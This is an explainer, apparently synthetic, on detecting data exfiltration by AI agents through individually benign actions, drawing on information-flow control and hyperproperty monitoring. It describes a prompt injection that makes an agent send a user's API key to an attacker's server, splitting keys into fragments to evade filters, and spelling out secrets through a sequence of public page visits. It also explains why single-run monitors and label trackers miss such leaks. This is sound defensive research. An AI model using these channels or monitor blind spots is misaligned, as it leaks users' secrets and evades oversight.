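# Detecting data exfiltration by AI agents through sequences of individually benign actions

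## How an agent can leak a secret without one suspicious step

Data exfiltration is the transfer of information out of a system to someone who has no right to it. AI agents create new opportunities for it because the same program reads private files and mailboxes, fetches web pages and sends messages. Detection is difficult when the secret leaves in several steps and the agent's user would approve of each step on its own. Computer scientists faced a version of this problem in the 1970s, when they tried to stop programs in settings such as military systems from passing classified data to people without clearance. They labeled data and made the labels travel with it. Designers of operating systems and web browsers later adopted the method, and researchers are now trying to apply it to agents, whose decisions come from a language model rather than from code that people can check line by line.

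### The agent loop

An agent is a language model that works in a loop. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes one turn of this loop. The program around the model passes it the conversation so far. The model either writes its final answer or requests a tool call, which is a single action such as reading a file, fetching a page or sending an email. The program carries out the call, appends the result to the conversation and repeats the loop. Only the program can run a tool call, so a guard can intervene there before the call runs.

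A trace is the record of one run. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) represents it as a sequence of steps, each consisting of a tool, its arguments and its result. A source is a point where secret or untrusted data enters the run, and a sink is an action whose effect an outsider can observe. Sending an email is a sink. Fetching a web page is both a source and a sink, because it brings in untrusted text and sends out an address the agent chose. The website receives that full address and commonly logs it, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains.

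Untrusted text matters because an attacker can hide instructions in it that the agent then follows, which is called indirect prompt injection. User instructions and web content reach the model as one stream of text, and the model can't reliably tell them apart. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) built web pages whose hidden description told the agent to "verify connectivity" by requesting an address with the user's API key in it. The user had asked only for a summary of the page. In 423 of 480 runs with a small open model, the agent sent a request to the attacker's server, and in 95% of the successful attacks the answer the user saw was harmless. The agent sent no such request in 120 control runs on clean pages.

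### Why most guards judge one call at a time

The obvious defence is a per-action guard, which judges each tool call by itself just before it runs. In August 2026, Anthropic made a classifier that works roughly this way the default for individual and team plans in Claude Code, its coding agent. The classifier replaces review by users, who had mostly stopped checking and approve 97% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). In a trial with 1,053 paid testers, people stopped 13.6% of planted dangerous commands, while the classifier stopped 89% of them. In Google's Chrome browser, a separate model vets each action the agent proposes, using only metadata about the action, according to Parker's *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (2025). Among research systems, *ToolSafe* (2026) builds a guardrail model that judges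 individual tool calls before they run.

A narrow view helps the guard decide quickly, since a long history takes time and money to read. It also limits the guard's exposure to the attacker's text, which is part of that history. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that the classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, including earlier ones, but no tool results, because hostile instructions arrive in the results. Its input therefore shows that the agent opened a certain file, but not what the file held. Anthropic acknowledges the loss of provenance and accepts it in exchange for resistance to injection.

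How well this works depends on the kind of leak. On 1,000 synthetic exfiltration attempts, many of them obfuscated, Anthropic's full pipeline missed 5.7%. Anthropic's examples are posting sensitive data to an outside server, pushing code to an untrusted destination and embedding credentials in a web address. Each of these is wrong in itself once someone works out what it does, so the result is weak evidence about leaks in which every call is acceptable. A few designs keep more state. *AIRGuard* (2026) records the agent's actions so that it can audit individually plausible steps together, and Chrome's design keeps, for each session, a set of sites the agent may read and a set it may act on.

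### Composition, fragments and choices

The simplest way for a sequence of actions to leak a secret is composition, in which a permitted read is followed by a permitted send. It needs no attacker. *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026) has 146 test tasks on data crossing internal and external boundaries. In one, the user asks the agent to read a project's environment file, summarise the configuration in a Google document and email the link to the operations team. The file contains credentials, and the leak happens because they are carried from one step to the next and end up in the document. The user asked for the read, the write and the email, so a guard has no reason to refuse any of these actions based on its type alone.

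That path can span a long conversation. In another task from the same benchmark, the agent handles credentials early on for a legitimate repair, and the surrounding software logs every call with its arguments. Much later, the user asks what the recent logs contain, and the agent repeats the credentials in its reply.

An agent can also cut a secret into fragments and send each in its own call. In half of their 480 runs, Lan and colleagues had the malicious page ask for exactly this: split the key into four pieces and put one in each of four requests. A piece such as "SECR" or "PI_K" can pass for routine telemetry. One filter that the team tried blocks addresses containing a random-looking value, but it examines only values longer than ten characters, so a four-character piece gets through by construction. (The team tested its filters against unsplit keys only.)

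Splitting the secret across requests made the attack less reliable. Averaged over the experiment's set-ups, at least one request reached the attacker in about 77% of split runs, compared with 99% of unsplit runs. The first request carried recognisable sensitive data in 26% of split runs, down from 97% without splitting. Lan and colleagues also report 16% for the first three requests together, which cannot be right under their own definition, because adding requests cannot lower that share. The direction of the effect is therefore more reliable than its size. The model was small, and the secret was directly visible in its context. A stronger model would probably keep better track of the pieces, though it might also resist the instruction more often.

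In the remaining form, choices, no call contains any piece of the secret. The agent conveys it by which calls it makes, or in what order. OpenAI's defence against leaks through web addresses shows why this is hard to prevent. Before an agent loads an address automatically, OpenAI's software checks that the exact address is already in an index of public pages, compiled by a crawler with no access to user data. An address with a stolen password on the end fails the check because the crawler is unlikely to have seen it. But Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on a security researcher's blog, describes a method that needs only 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit. The agent spells out the secret by visiting the matching pages in sequence. OpenAI's own paper on the check points out the same weakness.

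A small example makes the arithmetic plain. An agent knows a four-digit code, 7294. An outsider runs a website with ten public pages, one for each digit, and reads the site's log. The agent requests page 7, then page 2, then page 9, then page 4. Every address is in the public index and every request is an ordinary one. A choice among ten equally likely options carries log₂(10) bits of information, about 3.3, so no single request can give away more than that. The four together carry

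4 × log₂(10) = log₂(10,000) ≈ 13.3 bits,

which is the whole code.

Small obstacles reduce the leak but don't stop it. If the requests reach the log out of order, an outsider who finds 2, 4, 7 and 9 has only 24 codes to try instead of 10,000. Embrace The Red suggests preventing the agent from visiting the same address twice in a session. That would garble a code with repeated digits, such as 7727, but a code like 7294 would still leak intact.

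A guard that sees the whole trace might not do better here. The trace would show four visits to public pages, just as it would if the user had wanted to read those pages. Running the agent again with a different code would reveal the leak, because the visits would change with the code. Kim, Liu and colleagues (2026) reviewed 128 papers from 2023 to October 2025 in *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI*. They list call sequences and timing among the things an observer might exploit, and they knew of no prior work on such attacks against agents.

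### Labels and the join rule

A confidentiality label on a piece of data lists who may read it, and an integrity label records who may have influenced it. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a system that labels each piece of data as it enters the run. The system then copies the labels onto whatever the agent derives from that data, a step called taint tracking. In the next step, called information-flow control, the system compares the labels with the destination before each tool call and allows the call, blocks it or asks a human.

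The copying step needs a rule for mixtures. Suppose that A, B and C may read one text, that B, C and D may read another, and that an agent summarises both. A has no right to the second text and D has no right to the first, so the summary may go only to the people on both lists:

{A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}.

This combination is the join of the two labels. Labels are ordered from the least restrictive, which lets everyone read the data, to the most restrictive, which lets nobody read it. Neither {A, B, C} nor {B, C, D} ranks above the other in this order, but there is always a least restrictive label that is at least as strict as both. Here it is {B, C}. The label {B} would also be safe, but it would exclude C unnecessarily. An ordering in which any two labels have such a least upper bound, and also a greatest lower bound, is a lattice. For integrity, the join is the union instead. If A,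 B and C may have written one text and B, C and D the other, any of the four may have influenced the summary.

Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* set out this structure in 1976. Denning criticized the access controls of the time for governing immediate access to an object while ignoring the paths that a collection of access rights opens up, and her criticism applies almost word for word to per-action guards. Her remedy requires permitted flows to be transitive. If data may flow from class X to class Y, and from Y to Z, then the rules must also allow it to flow from X to Z; otherwise a program could make a forbidden transfer through two permitted ones. Under that condition, a sequence of operations is secure whenever each operation in it is secure. A guard can therefore still judge one call at a time, because the data's label records the relevant history. The result covers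 transfers such as copying, parameter passing and sending messages, but Denning excluded covert channels, such as a process's effect on machine load.

Taint tracking applies directly to composition and fragments, provided that the labels survive processing by the model. The summary of the environment file inherits the label of the credentials, and so does a four-character piece of a key, however harmless it looks. Lan and colleagues recommend taint tracking for agents for much the same reason, since it goes by where data came from and ignores how it looks.

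A label check works the same way whatever the agent's reason for acting. In Microsoft's example, Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered email. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales figures, and Marco, who may not see them yet, has written out of curiosity. Once the agent has read both messages, its draft carries a label listing who may read it, {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, and the check stops the agent from replying to Marco on its own. Here the agent was only being too helpful, but the check would also have stopped it if it had been following an injected instruction or pursuing its own aim. Anthropic lists overeagerness, honest mistakes, prompt injection and a misaligned model as separate threats, but its defence against all of them is to block the action. Unlike a classifier, a label check follows fixed rules, though its results are only reliable if other parts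 of the system are correct. *APPA* (2026), a label-based design that treats everything the model proposes as untrusted, still relies on its own monitor, the declared behaviour of each tool and the registered routines that clean or convert data.

### Explicit and implicit flows

Denning also drew the distinction on which the choice channel turns. In an explicit flow, the program copies or transforms secret data into an output:

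`b := a`

Anyone who reads b afterwards learns a. In an implicit flow, the secret decides whether an action happens:

`if a = 0 then b := 0`

If b started at some other value, an observer who later finds b unchanged knows that a was not zero. Information has moved from a to b even though the assignment never ran, and tracking labels through copies would miss it because nothing was copied.

An agent that pastes the code 7294 into an email creates an explicit flow. The four page requests create an implicit flow, since the addresses are public strings that existed before the agent learned the code. A tracker that passes on labels only when data is copied will not label the requests secret. A more cautious tracker gives every output of the model the combined label of everything in its context, which is the default that Costa and colleagues describe. It would block all four requests, along with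 any other request to a public website that the model made after reading the code, including those the user needs. Preventing implicit flows entirely would require noninterference, meaning that nothing an outsider observes may depend on the secret, and Costa and colleagues consider that too restrictive for working agents.

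## Theory: what a monitor of one run cannot decide

Noninterference constrains how the runs of a system relate to one another, so the record of a single run is not enough to check it. Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer defined it in 1982 for computers that people with high and low clearances share. Deleting every command from the high users had to leave what the low users observed unchanged. For an agent, the secrets it reads correspond to the high users' commands, and the outsider corresponds to a low user. Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, write the requirement in terms of the set T of all traces that a deterministic system can produce:

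for every t in T there is a t′ in T with secret(t′) = ∅ and public(t′) = public(t).

Here secret(t) is the sequence of secret inputs in the trace t, and public(t) is the sequence of inputs and outputs that an outsider can observe. The agent that spelled out the code 7294 in four page visits would satisfy the requirement only if it could also make those visits, after the same user request, without reading any code. It can't, but a monitor can't tell that from the log of the leaking run.

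A closely related requirement, observational determinism, is easier to work with. Any two runs with the same public inputs must have the same public outputs:

for all t, t′ in T: if in(t) = in(t′), then out(t) = out(t′).

Two runs of the page-visiting agent, one with the code 7294 and one with 1358, prove a violation.

### What the history of one run can settle

Many other security rules apply to each run separately. A trace property is a set of permitted traces, and a system satisfies it if every trace it can produce is in the set. One of Clarkson and Schneider's examples is the rule that a system may not write to the network after reading a file. *Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) describes a two-state monitor for nearly the same rule. It starts in "no file read", moves to "file read" at the first read, and from then on rejects any attempt to send.

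This rule is a safety property, which means that every violation shows up in some finite beginning of the trace and that nothing later can repair it. Schneider proved that a monitor can enforce only safety properties if all it does is watch a run and halt it. The argument has three steps:

1. The monitor decides about each run from that run alone, so its policy must be a condition on individual traces.
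2. The monitor can't look ahead. If a partial run is unacceptable, the monitor has to stop it there, even if some continuation would have made it acceptable, because the run might end at that point. A rejected beginning therefore rules out all its continuations.
3. The monitor must reject a bad run after finitely many steps, since otherwise it never acts.

A condition on individual traces that meets the last two demands is a safety property. But a monitor can't enforce every safety property, because some forbid actions it has no power to stop. *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited*, by Basin, Jugé and colleagues, refines the result by separating the actions a monitor can prevent from those it can only observe.

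Safety properties cover many of the leaks that occur through sequences of actions. *Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) splits what a user authorizes an agent to do into rules about intent, purpose, provenance, consent and delegation. It proves that all of these except purpose are safety properties of single traces, provided that provenance is treated as a rule about the path data takes. Each of these four rules is broken at an identifiable step in the run: an action outside the user's task, a write of data from an untrusted source, a disclosure beyond what the user agreed to, or a use of delegated authority without a fresh check.

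Rules on cumulative disclosure show why history matters. Let c(a) be the amount that an action a discloses, which is never negative, and let B be the most that the user has agreed to. The rule is

c(a₁) + c(a₂) + … + c(aₙ) ≤ B for every n.

Each action can be small enough to pass by itself. But once the sum exceeds B, it stays above B, so a monitor that keeps a running total can refuse the action that would push the total over B. This would catch a key that leaves in four pieces during one run, provided the monitor can recognize the pieces. Memory is also enough for a monitor to catch the credentials copied into a shared document, as taint tracking does.

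Pandey and colleagues tried this with Qwen3-30B, an open model, acting as a calendar agent. Without a guard, the agent disclosed more in total than the user had agreed to in 22 of 60 runs. With a guard that compared each action with the declared purpose, it still did so in 20 of 60, which is no measurable improvement. Checking the purpose of each action therefore did almost nothing to stop a leak that builds up over several. A guard that kept a running total of what had been disclosed prevented every failure and blocked nothing in 120 harmless control runs. Its perfect prevention rate is expected, because it enforces the same limit that defines a failure. A second model, Gemma-4, never overshared in the same task, so how often the problem occurs depends on the model.

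### Requirements on sets of runs

Noninterference does not fit this scheme. Schneider credits John McLean with the 1994 proof that information flow is not a trace property. Whether a secret influences an output in one run depends partly on what the output would have been in other runs. Clarkson and Schneider generalized such requirements as hyperproperties. A hyperproperty is a set of sets of traces, where each inner set contains all the traces that one system allowed by the policy can produce.

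Safety extends to hyperproperties. Any violation of a k-safety hyperproperty can be shown with k finite traces, and no further runs can undo it. Ordinary safety is the case k = 1. Observational determinism is 2-safety because each violation is a pair of runs with the same public inputs but different public outputs.

Larger values of k matter when a secret leaks in fragments. Clarkson and Schneider consider a system that splits a secret into k shares, all of which are needed to reconstruct it, and that must never output all k across its runs. If an agent sends the four pieces of a key in four separate sessions, no session contains the whole leak, so a monitor that starts afresh each time will miss it. A monitor that keeps a record of earlier sessions can count the pieces. Checking this hyperproperty therefore requires only a longer memory, whereas checking observational determinism requires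 comparing the agent's behavior when given one secret with its behavior when given another.

Such leaks also occur in ordinary software. *The Complexity of Monitoring Hyperproperties* (Bonakdarpour and Finkbeiner, 2021) describes one that Bonakdarpour found in EDAS, a conference management system. A table listed four of his papers. The "session" column read "not yet assigned" for an accepted paper and was empty for a rejected one. Two papers at a different conference were still pending, but their session columns differed in the same way. Comparing the rows revealed the decisions on both pending papers before the official notification, although no row looked wrong by itself.

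### The scheduling assistant and the self-agreement proof

Pure noninterference would bar an assistant from using any private information in its answers, so Pandey and colleagues start from a requirement that allows exceptions. In their example, a user asks an assistant to find a time for a team meeting and permits it to share when the user is free or busy. The assistant's proposal may depend on which slots are free, but not on why a slot is busy.

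For a trace t, let low(t) be the declared purpose and other public inputs, hi(t) the private context that the agent may read, and obs(t) what it discloses. A declassification function D extracts the part of the private context that the purpose allows the agent to use, here the free or busy status of each slot. A second function, α, keeps the parts of a disclosure that matter to the policy, such as the slots offered, any reason given and the recipient. A set S of traces satisfies the purpose rule if

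for all t, t′ in S: if low(t) = low(t′) and D(hi(t)) = D(hi(t′)), then α(obs(t)) = α(obs(t′)).

Under this rule, two runs that agree on everything the agent may take into account must also agree on what it discloses. If D extracts nothing and α keeps everything, the rule reduces to observational determinism.

Suppose two calendars have the same free slots, including 10 and 11. In one, a certain busy slot is an ordinary meeting, and the assistant offers slot 10. In the other, the same busy slot is a confidential interview, and the assistant offers slot 11. Each proposal correctly answers the request, but together the two runs break the rule, and a colleague who knows the pattern can tell from the offered slot whether an interview is taking place. Pandey and colleagues reproduced this pair in LangGraph, a widely used agent framework. A guard that checked permissions, purpose labels, provenance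 and consent allowed all three steps in both runs.

The proof that no better guard of this kind would help takes only a few lines. Let S contain a single trace t. The rule then has only one pair to test, namely t with itself. Since

α(obs(t)) = α(obs(t)),

the rule holds. Nothing about t entered the argument, so every one-trace system satisfies the rule, including the system whose only run offers slot 11.

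Theorem 3 of Pandey and colleagues shows that if a monitor decides from one trace whether to raise an alarm, and never raises a false alarm, it detects no violations. A false alarm here is an alarm on a trace that satisfies the rule by itself. Every trace does, so the monitor can never raise an alarm.

The proof makes no assumption about how the monitor reaches its verdict. It covers a language model that reads the complete history just as it covers a fixed rule about single calls. None of the six agent guardrails that Pandey and colleagues surveyed compares two runs, and that includes the label-based system of Costa and colleagues. (The survey goes by published designs. Pandey and colleagues did not run the code.)

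The purpose rule is always a 2-safety property, and it is not a trace property if and only if there are two traces a and b that agree on the public inputs and the permitted context but differ in what they disclose (Theorem 1). If the rule were a trace property, it would amount to a list of permitted traces, and both a and b would be on it because each satisfies the rule alone. A system that can produce both would then comply, but a and b together violate the rule. If no such pair exists, the public inputs and permitted context already determine every disclosure, and the rule forbids nothing. Such a pair exists for any assistant with some freedom in how it answers.

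### Agents that choose at random

A language model's output is usually partly random, so the same calendar can lead to different offers. An assistant that chooses at random between slots 10 and 11 reveals nothing about the interview, but it breaks the purpose rule as written, because two runs with the same permitted inputs can offer different slots.

Comparing only the possible outputs would be too lenient. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that outputs 0, 1 or a secret bit, choosing among the three at random. Both outputs are possible whatever the secret is, but if the three choices are equally likely, the output matches the secret two times out of three. For a random agent, the disclosure must therefore be statistically independent of the rest of the private context, given the public inputs and the permitted context.

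Theorem 4 shows that a monitor can't decide this from one run either. Suppose the monitor observes a single offer of slot 11. The coin-tossing assistant could have made that offer, and so could an assistant that offers slot 11 only when there is an interview, so whichever verdict the monitor gives is wrong for one of them. Pandey and colleagues construct such a pair for any single observation with positive probability.

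Repeated runs help, although they never bring certainty. With an interview in the calendar, the coin-tossing assistant has only a 1 in 1,024 chance of offering slot 11 ten times in a row, so ten runs are usually enough to tell these two assistants apart. Detecting a weaker leak takes far more runs. If the interview raises the frequency of slot 11 from 50% to 51%, a standard test at the 5% significance level needs about 39,000 runs with each calendar for an 80% chance of detecting the difference. However many runs an auditor collects, they could still miss an even smaller leak.

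### How much depends on the meaning of "false alarm"

The proof of Theorem 3 is short because it follows mostly from the definition of a false alarm. An alarm on a trace counts as false if some compliant system could have produced that trace, regardless of what the actual agent would have done with a different secret.

Imagine an assistant whose code contains the line

`if reason = interview then offer 11 else offer 10`

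A monitor with access to this code could raise an alarm at the offer of slot 11, and its operator would call the alarm correct. Under the theorem's definition the alarm is false, because an assistant that always offers slot 11 would have left the same trace. So the theorem rules out a monitor that works for every possible agent from the trace alone, but not one that is built for a particular agent and has further information about it. Schneider limited his 2000 result in the same way. It does not cover mechanisms that have information about alternative runs, and he left open how much power such information gives.

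Nobody can determine a rule like that by inspecting a language model's weights, but an operator can run the model again. After the assistant has offered slot 11, the operator replaces the interview with an ordinary meeting, keeps everything else the same and checks which slot the assistant offers. The original run and the modified one form the pair that the purpose rule requires.

Chalupa, Henzinger and Oliveira da Costa (2025), in *Monitoring Hyperproperties over Observed and Constructed Traces*, measured how much constructed runs can help. They simulated a robot that moves on a 10-by-10 grid towards a secret target cell, while an outsider observes only which areas of the grid it crosses. The public input was a list of areas the robot had to pass through. A monitor that could detect the leak only when two observed runs conflicted could need hundreds of runs, and it often found nothing within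 the limit of 2,048. When the list had more than nine areas, it never found the leak, because two runs hardly ever had the same list. A monitor that could also sample new runs with the same public input typically found the leak after one or two observed runs.

An agent's public input includes the user's whole request, which is far longer than nine areas, so matching pairs will probably be rare in ordinary logs. Constructed runs therefore seem more promising, though they are harder to produce for an agent than for this robot. The robot followed a fixed, deterministic strategy, and trying it on another input had no side effects. Rerunning an agent requires simulating its mailbox and other tools so that it doesn't send the email twice. Someone must also decide which data is secret and write a plausible substitute, and the model's randomness brings back the statistical problem.

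Pandey and colleagues list three ways to detect violations of the purpose rule: compare runs as they happen, audit the agent offline with varied secrets, or accept false alarms. The cautious tracker that gives every output the label of the whole context accepts false alarms. Schneider had already noted that monitors said to prevent information flow actually enforce some stricter policy. Violations can also be prevented by having the assistant compose its proposal from the free and busy times alone. The hidden reason then can't affect the result, but this requires an extra run and loses whatever the withheld context would have contributed.

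### Monitoring many runs

Comparing runs systematically requires a language for stating what to compare. *Temporal Logics for Hyperproperties* (2014) introduced HyperLTL, which extends a standard logic for describing how one run unfolds over time with variables that stand for whole traces. A version of observational determinism reads

∀π. ∀π′. (o_π = o_π′) W (i_π ≠ i_π′).

For every two traces π and π′, the outputs o must stay equal until the public inputs i differ. The symbol W means "weak until", which also allows the inputs never to differ.

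*Monitoring Hyperproperties* (Finkbeiner, Hahn and colleagues, 2018) shows that what a monitor can conclude depends on the quantifiers at the front of the formula. Apart from trivial cases, a monitor can refute a formula that uses only "for all" but can never confirm it. One conflicting pair of runs refutes the formula permanently, but even after a million consistent runs, the next one could conflict. A monitor that checks such a formula can therefore report leaks but can't certify that an agent is free of them.

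A monitor can never reach a verdict on most formulas that mix "for all" with "there exists" if the number of runs has no limit. For example, generalized noninterference, a version of noninterference for nondeterministic systems, requires that for any runs t and t′ there is a third run with the public events of t and the secret inputs of t′. If the third run is missing from the log, the monitor can't report a violation, because a later run may supply it. Even if every pair so far has its third run, the monitor can't report that the property holds, because a later run may form a new pair that lacks one. If the number of runs is fixed in advance, the monitor can reach a verdict, but only about those runs.

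Treating an incomplete log as complete leads to errors in practice. Chalupa and colleagues checked generalized noninterference on 30 small programs, using 200 recorded runs of each. The monitor that used only the recorded runs wrongly reported violations in seven programs. In those seven, a search through the program's possible paths found the missing runs. The search needs the program's code, so it is hard to apply to a language model.

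Memory and time are further obstacles. A monitor of one run can discard each step after updating its state, but a monitor of hyperproperties may have to keep every past run to compare with future ones. The number of pairs grows with the square of the number of runs. In one hardware test by Finkbeiner and colleagues, 1,000 runs led to 499,500 pairwise checks, which took about 17 seconds. Storing shared beginnings only once, in a tree, and skipping redundant comparisons cut this to 127 checks and 1.6 seconds. *Efficient Monitoring of Hyperproperties using Prefix Trees* (Finkbeiner, Hahn and colleagues, 2021) describes the method in detail and reports that building the monitor, which happens only once, can take time doubly exponential in the length of the formula.

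How the log is stored also affects how hard it is to check. Bonakdarpour and Finkbeiner proved that, for a fixed formula and a log stored as a tree, the working memory a check needs grows only with the logarithm of the log's size. Merging shared endings as well as shared beginnings makes the log smaller, but formulas that mix quantifiers then become much harder to check. Agent traces may benefit less from either method than hardware traces do, because two conversations that differ in one word early on soon have little text in common.

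Intervening is harder than detecting. *Runtime Enforcement of Hyperproperties* (Coenen, Finkbeiner and colleagues, 2022) points out that halting a run can itself release information. If a monitor silences the scheduling assistant whenever the busy slot is an interview, a colleague can learn from the silence what slot 11 would have revealed. The paper therefore studies enforcers that correct the output and let the system continue. It gives a method for a fixed number of parallel runs, but proves that the general problem is undecidable (no algorithm solves every case) when runs arrive one after another without limit, as an assistant's sessions do. Algorithms do exist for safety hyperproperties such as observational determinism, and for the weaker goal of correcting only the current session.

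## Theory: what labels can guarantee on a single run

Some label trackers provably enforce noninterference even though they watch only one run at a time. The theorem of Pandey and colleagues doesn't rule this out, because these trackers allow false alarms. A tracker enforces a rule that each run obeys or breaks by itself, and the rule is strict enough that any set of runs obeying it satisfies noninterference.

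Schneider's rule against sending anything after reading a file is a crude example. If two runs of a deterministic agent start from the same request and differ only in what a private file contains, they are identical until the agent reads the file. After that, neither can send anything, so an outsider sees the same messages in both. But the rule also blocks messages unrelated to the file, such as a lunch order. Label tracking aims to stop fewer runs while still preventing leaks.

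### The assignment that never runs

To handle implicit flows, a tracker labels the program's current position as well as its data. This program-counter label is secret while the program is inside a conditional that tests a secret, and the tracker attaches it to everything the program writes there. In the earlier example, `if a = 0 then b := 0`, the assignment would make b secret.

That isn't enough. A small program that goes back to Fenton and Denning in the 1970s shows why. In this version the only secret is whether the user has a job interview:

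```
1  a := yes;  b := yes
2  if interview = yes then a := no
3  if a = yes then b := no
4  send b
```

| Line | If there is an interview | If there is none |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | a and b are "yes" and public | a and b are "yes" and public |
| 2 | a becomes "no" and secret | no assignment; a stays "yes" and public |
| 3 | no assignment; b stays "yes" and public | b becomes "no" and stays public, because a is public |
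| 4 | sends "yes" | sends "no" |

The outsider receives the right answer with a public label in both cases. In each column, the secret gets past the tracker at the line where no assignment runs. With no interview, for example, line 2 assigns nothing, so the tracker has nothing to label. But a is still "yes" only because there is no interview, and line 3 passes that information to b.

An analysis of the program text would show that line 2 might change `a`, and would label `a` as secret in both cases, but a monitor observes only the lines that run. Decisions made inside a language model have no program text to analyse.

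### Stopping the program before it can leak

Austin and Flanagan (2009), in *Efficient purely-dynamic information flow analysis*, closed this gap without analysing the program text. Under their no-sensitive-upgrade rule, a program may not change a public variable while its program-counter label is secret. In general, an assignment to x may run only if

pc ⊑ label(x),

where pc is the program-counter label and ⊑ means "is at most as restrictive as". If the condition fails, the monitor stops the program.

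If there is an interview in the calendar, the program above now stops at line 2, because that line would change the public variable a inside a secret conditional. If there is no interview, the program finishes and sends "no". It can no longer send two different answers, but an outsider who expects a message and gets none can still infer that there is an interview. The rule guarantees only termination-insensitive noninterference, which means that if two runs differ only in their secrets and both finish, their public results agree, though whether a run finishes may depend on the secret.

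This exception matters less than it might seem, because a stopped program can't go on to leak the next bit. Without the rule, a program could repeat the four-line trick for each bit of a four-digit code and send the whole code in 14 messages. With the rule, a program that sends messages as it runs can still count:

```
for n from 0000 to 9999:
    send n
    if code = n then a := no
```

If the code is 7294, the monitor stops the program just after it has sent 7294, and the outsider reads the code from the last message. That takes 7,295 messages instead of 14. Each extra digit makes the count ten times longer, and for a random 128-bit key the count would never finish in practice. The protection disappears if something restarts the program after each stop with information about what happened.

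The rule also stops harmless programs. If line 2 were the whole program and nothing ever used `a` again, the monitor would still stop it. *Generalizing Permissive-Upgrade in Dynamic Information Flow Analysis* (Bichhawat, Rajani and colleagues, 2015) points this out and says such false positives occur because the monitor examines only the executed trace.

Austin and Flanagan (2010), in *Permissive dynamic information flow analysis*, proposed a less strict rule. It allows the assignment in line 2 but marks a as partially leaked, meaning that a's label would have been public if the branch had not run. The monitor then stops the program only when it branches on a, here in line 3. This happens even if the program would never have sent anything afterwards, so there are still false positives, but fewer. Austin and Flanagan defined the rule for two labels, secret and public, and for combinations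 of such pairs. Bichhawat and colleagues extended it to arbitrary lattices.

Labels can leak secrets. After line 2, the label on `a` is secret if there is an interview and public if there is none, so a program that could read the label could determine whether there is an interview without reading the data. Buiras, Stefan and Russo (2014), in *On Dynamic Flow-Sensitive Floating-Label Systems*, warn that naively adding labels that change during a run can open a high-bandwidth covert channel. An agent could likewise open a covert channel by telling an outsider why the monitor refused a message.

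### Label creep

Most false alarms in an agent have a simpler cause. The cautious tracker gives everything the model writes the combined label of the whole conversation. Suppose Alex's agent has read a performance review that only Alex may see. If Alex then asks the agent to look up the cafeteria menu and post it to the team, the tracker blocks the post because it carries the review's label, even though the menu is public. This is label creep, the spread of restrictive labels until the system blocks most useful actions. Costa and colleagues call it a fundamental limitation of the basic agent loop with taint tracking.

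One remedy is to keep restricted data out of the conversation. The program around the model can store a tool's result in a variable and show the model only the variable's name, which the model can then pass to another tool. According to Costa and colleagues, this suits data-independent tasks, which are those that one fixed sequence of tool calls and one final response can solve whatever the data are. An example is forwarding the latest three emails to a colleague. An agent that sticks to the fixed sequence also closes the choice channel, since it makes the same calls whatever the emails contain. Completing the tasks on today's to-do list is not data-independent, because the model has to read the list to know what to do next.

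### Explicit secrecy

For tasks of the second sort, Costa and colleagues give up noninterference and settle for explicit secrecy. Their definition treats all the data that tools can read or change as one datastore d, with a secret part and a public part. Suppose that a run starting from the datastore d₁ has made some tool calls, and let g be the combined effect of those calls. The run satisfies explicit secrecy if

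g(d₁) and g(d₂) have the same public part

for every datastore d₂ that differs from d₁ only in its secrets. In other words, take the calls that the agent actually made, repeat them with different secrets, and check whether the public outcome changes.

If the agent calls a tool that forwards the file with the code 7294 to an outsider, repeating the call with a different code in the file changes what the outsider receives, so the run fails. The four page visits pass because repeating them adds the same four lines to the website's log whatever the code is. The agent would have visited different pages if the code had been different, but the definition doesn't depend on what the agent would have done.

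Taken literally, the definition would also allow an email in which the model itself had typed 7294, because the repetition keeps the arguments the model wrote. The label check is stricter in this case because it gives text the model writes the label of the whole conversation.

The check is looser when the model refers to stored data by name. Suppose ten variables each hold the address of one public page, and the model has read the secret code. The confidentiality policy in Costa and colleagues' paper checks the labels on a call's arguments, and a stored address keeps its own public label. The policy would therefore allow the agent to visit pages 7, 2, 9 and 4 in turn, although the code determined each choice.

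Costa and colleagues accept implicit flows because ruling them out would be too restrictive. They argue that noninterference in their setting would amount to forbidding any call with public effects after any call that may read a secret, which is close to the crude rule at the start of this section. They point out that web browsers and TaintDroid, a tracker for Android phones, made the same compromise. They also expect an outsider who sees the sequence of calls to infer only limited information. This holds for a single choice among a few options, but the amount an outsider can infer grows with every call.

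### The LLMbda calculus

*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) keeps noninterference, although this stops more runs. The calculus is a very small programming language for describing agents. A program can send data to a language model, run the reply as code, branch off a temporary copy of the conversation, or clear the conversation. Branching off and clearing the conversation both limit label creep, because a program can ask about restricted data in a side conversation and then discard that conversation. The answer keeps its restrictive label, but the main conversation does not acquire it.

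The conversation has its own label, and sending restricted data to the model raises it. Code in the model's reply runs with that label as its program-counter label, so code the model writes after reading a secret can produce only secret results.

The no-sensitive-upgrade rule also applies to the conversation. In one of the paper's examples, a program tells the model to remember that x is false. If a secret is true, the program then tells the model to set x to true. Finally, it asks the model for x. The interpreter stops the program at the conditional message. If it had let the message through and labelled the conversation secret, the run in which the secret is false would still have ended with a public answer, as in the interview program.

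The main theorem covers every program in the language, with one extra condition for programs that relabel data. Because a model's replies are partly random, the theorem compares probabilities rather than single results. For each secret, consider how likely each public result is. If some runs never finish, these probabilities add up to less than 1. Two such lists of probabilities, μ and ν, are compatible if there is a third list ω with

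μ ≤ ω, ν ≤ ω and a total of at most 1.

The theorem states that whenever two starting points differ only in their secrets, their lists of public results are compatible.

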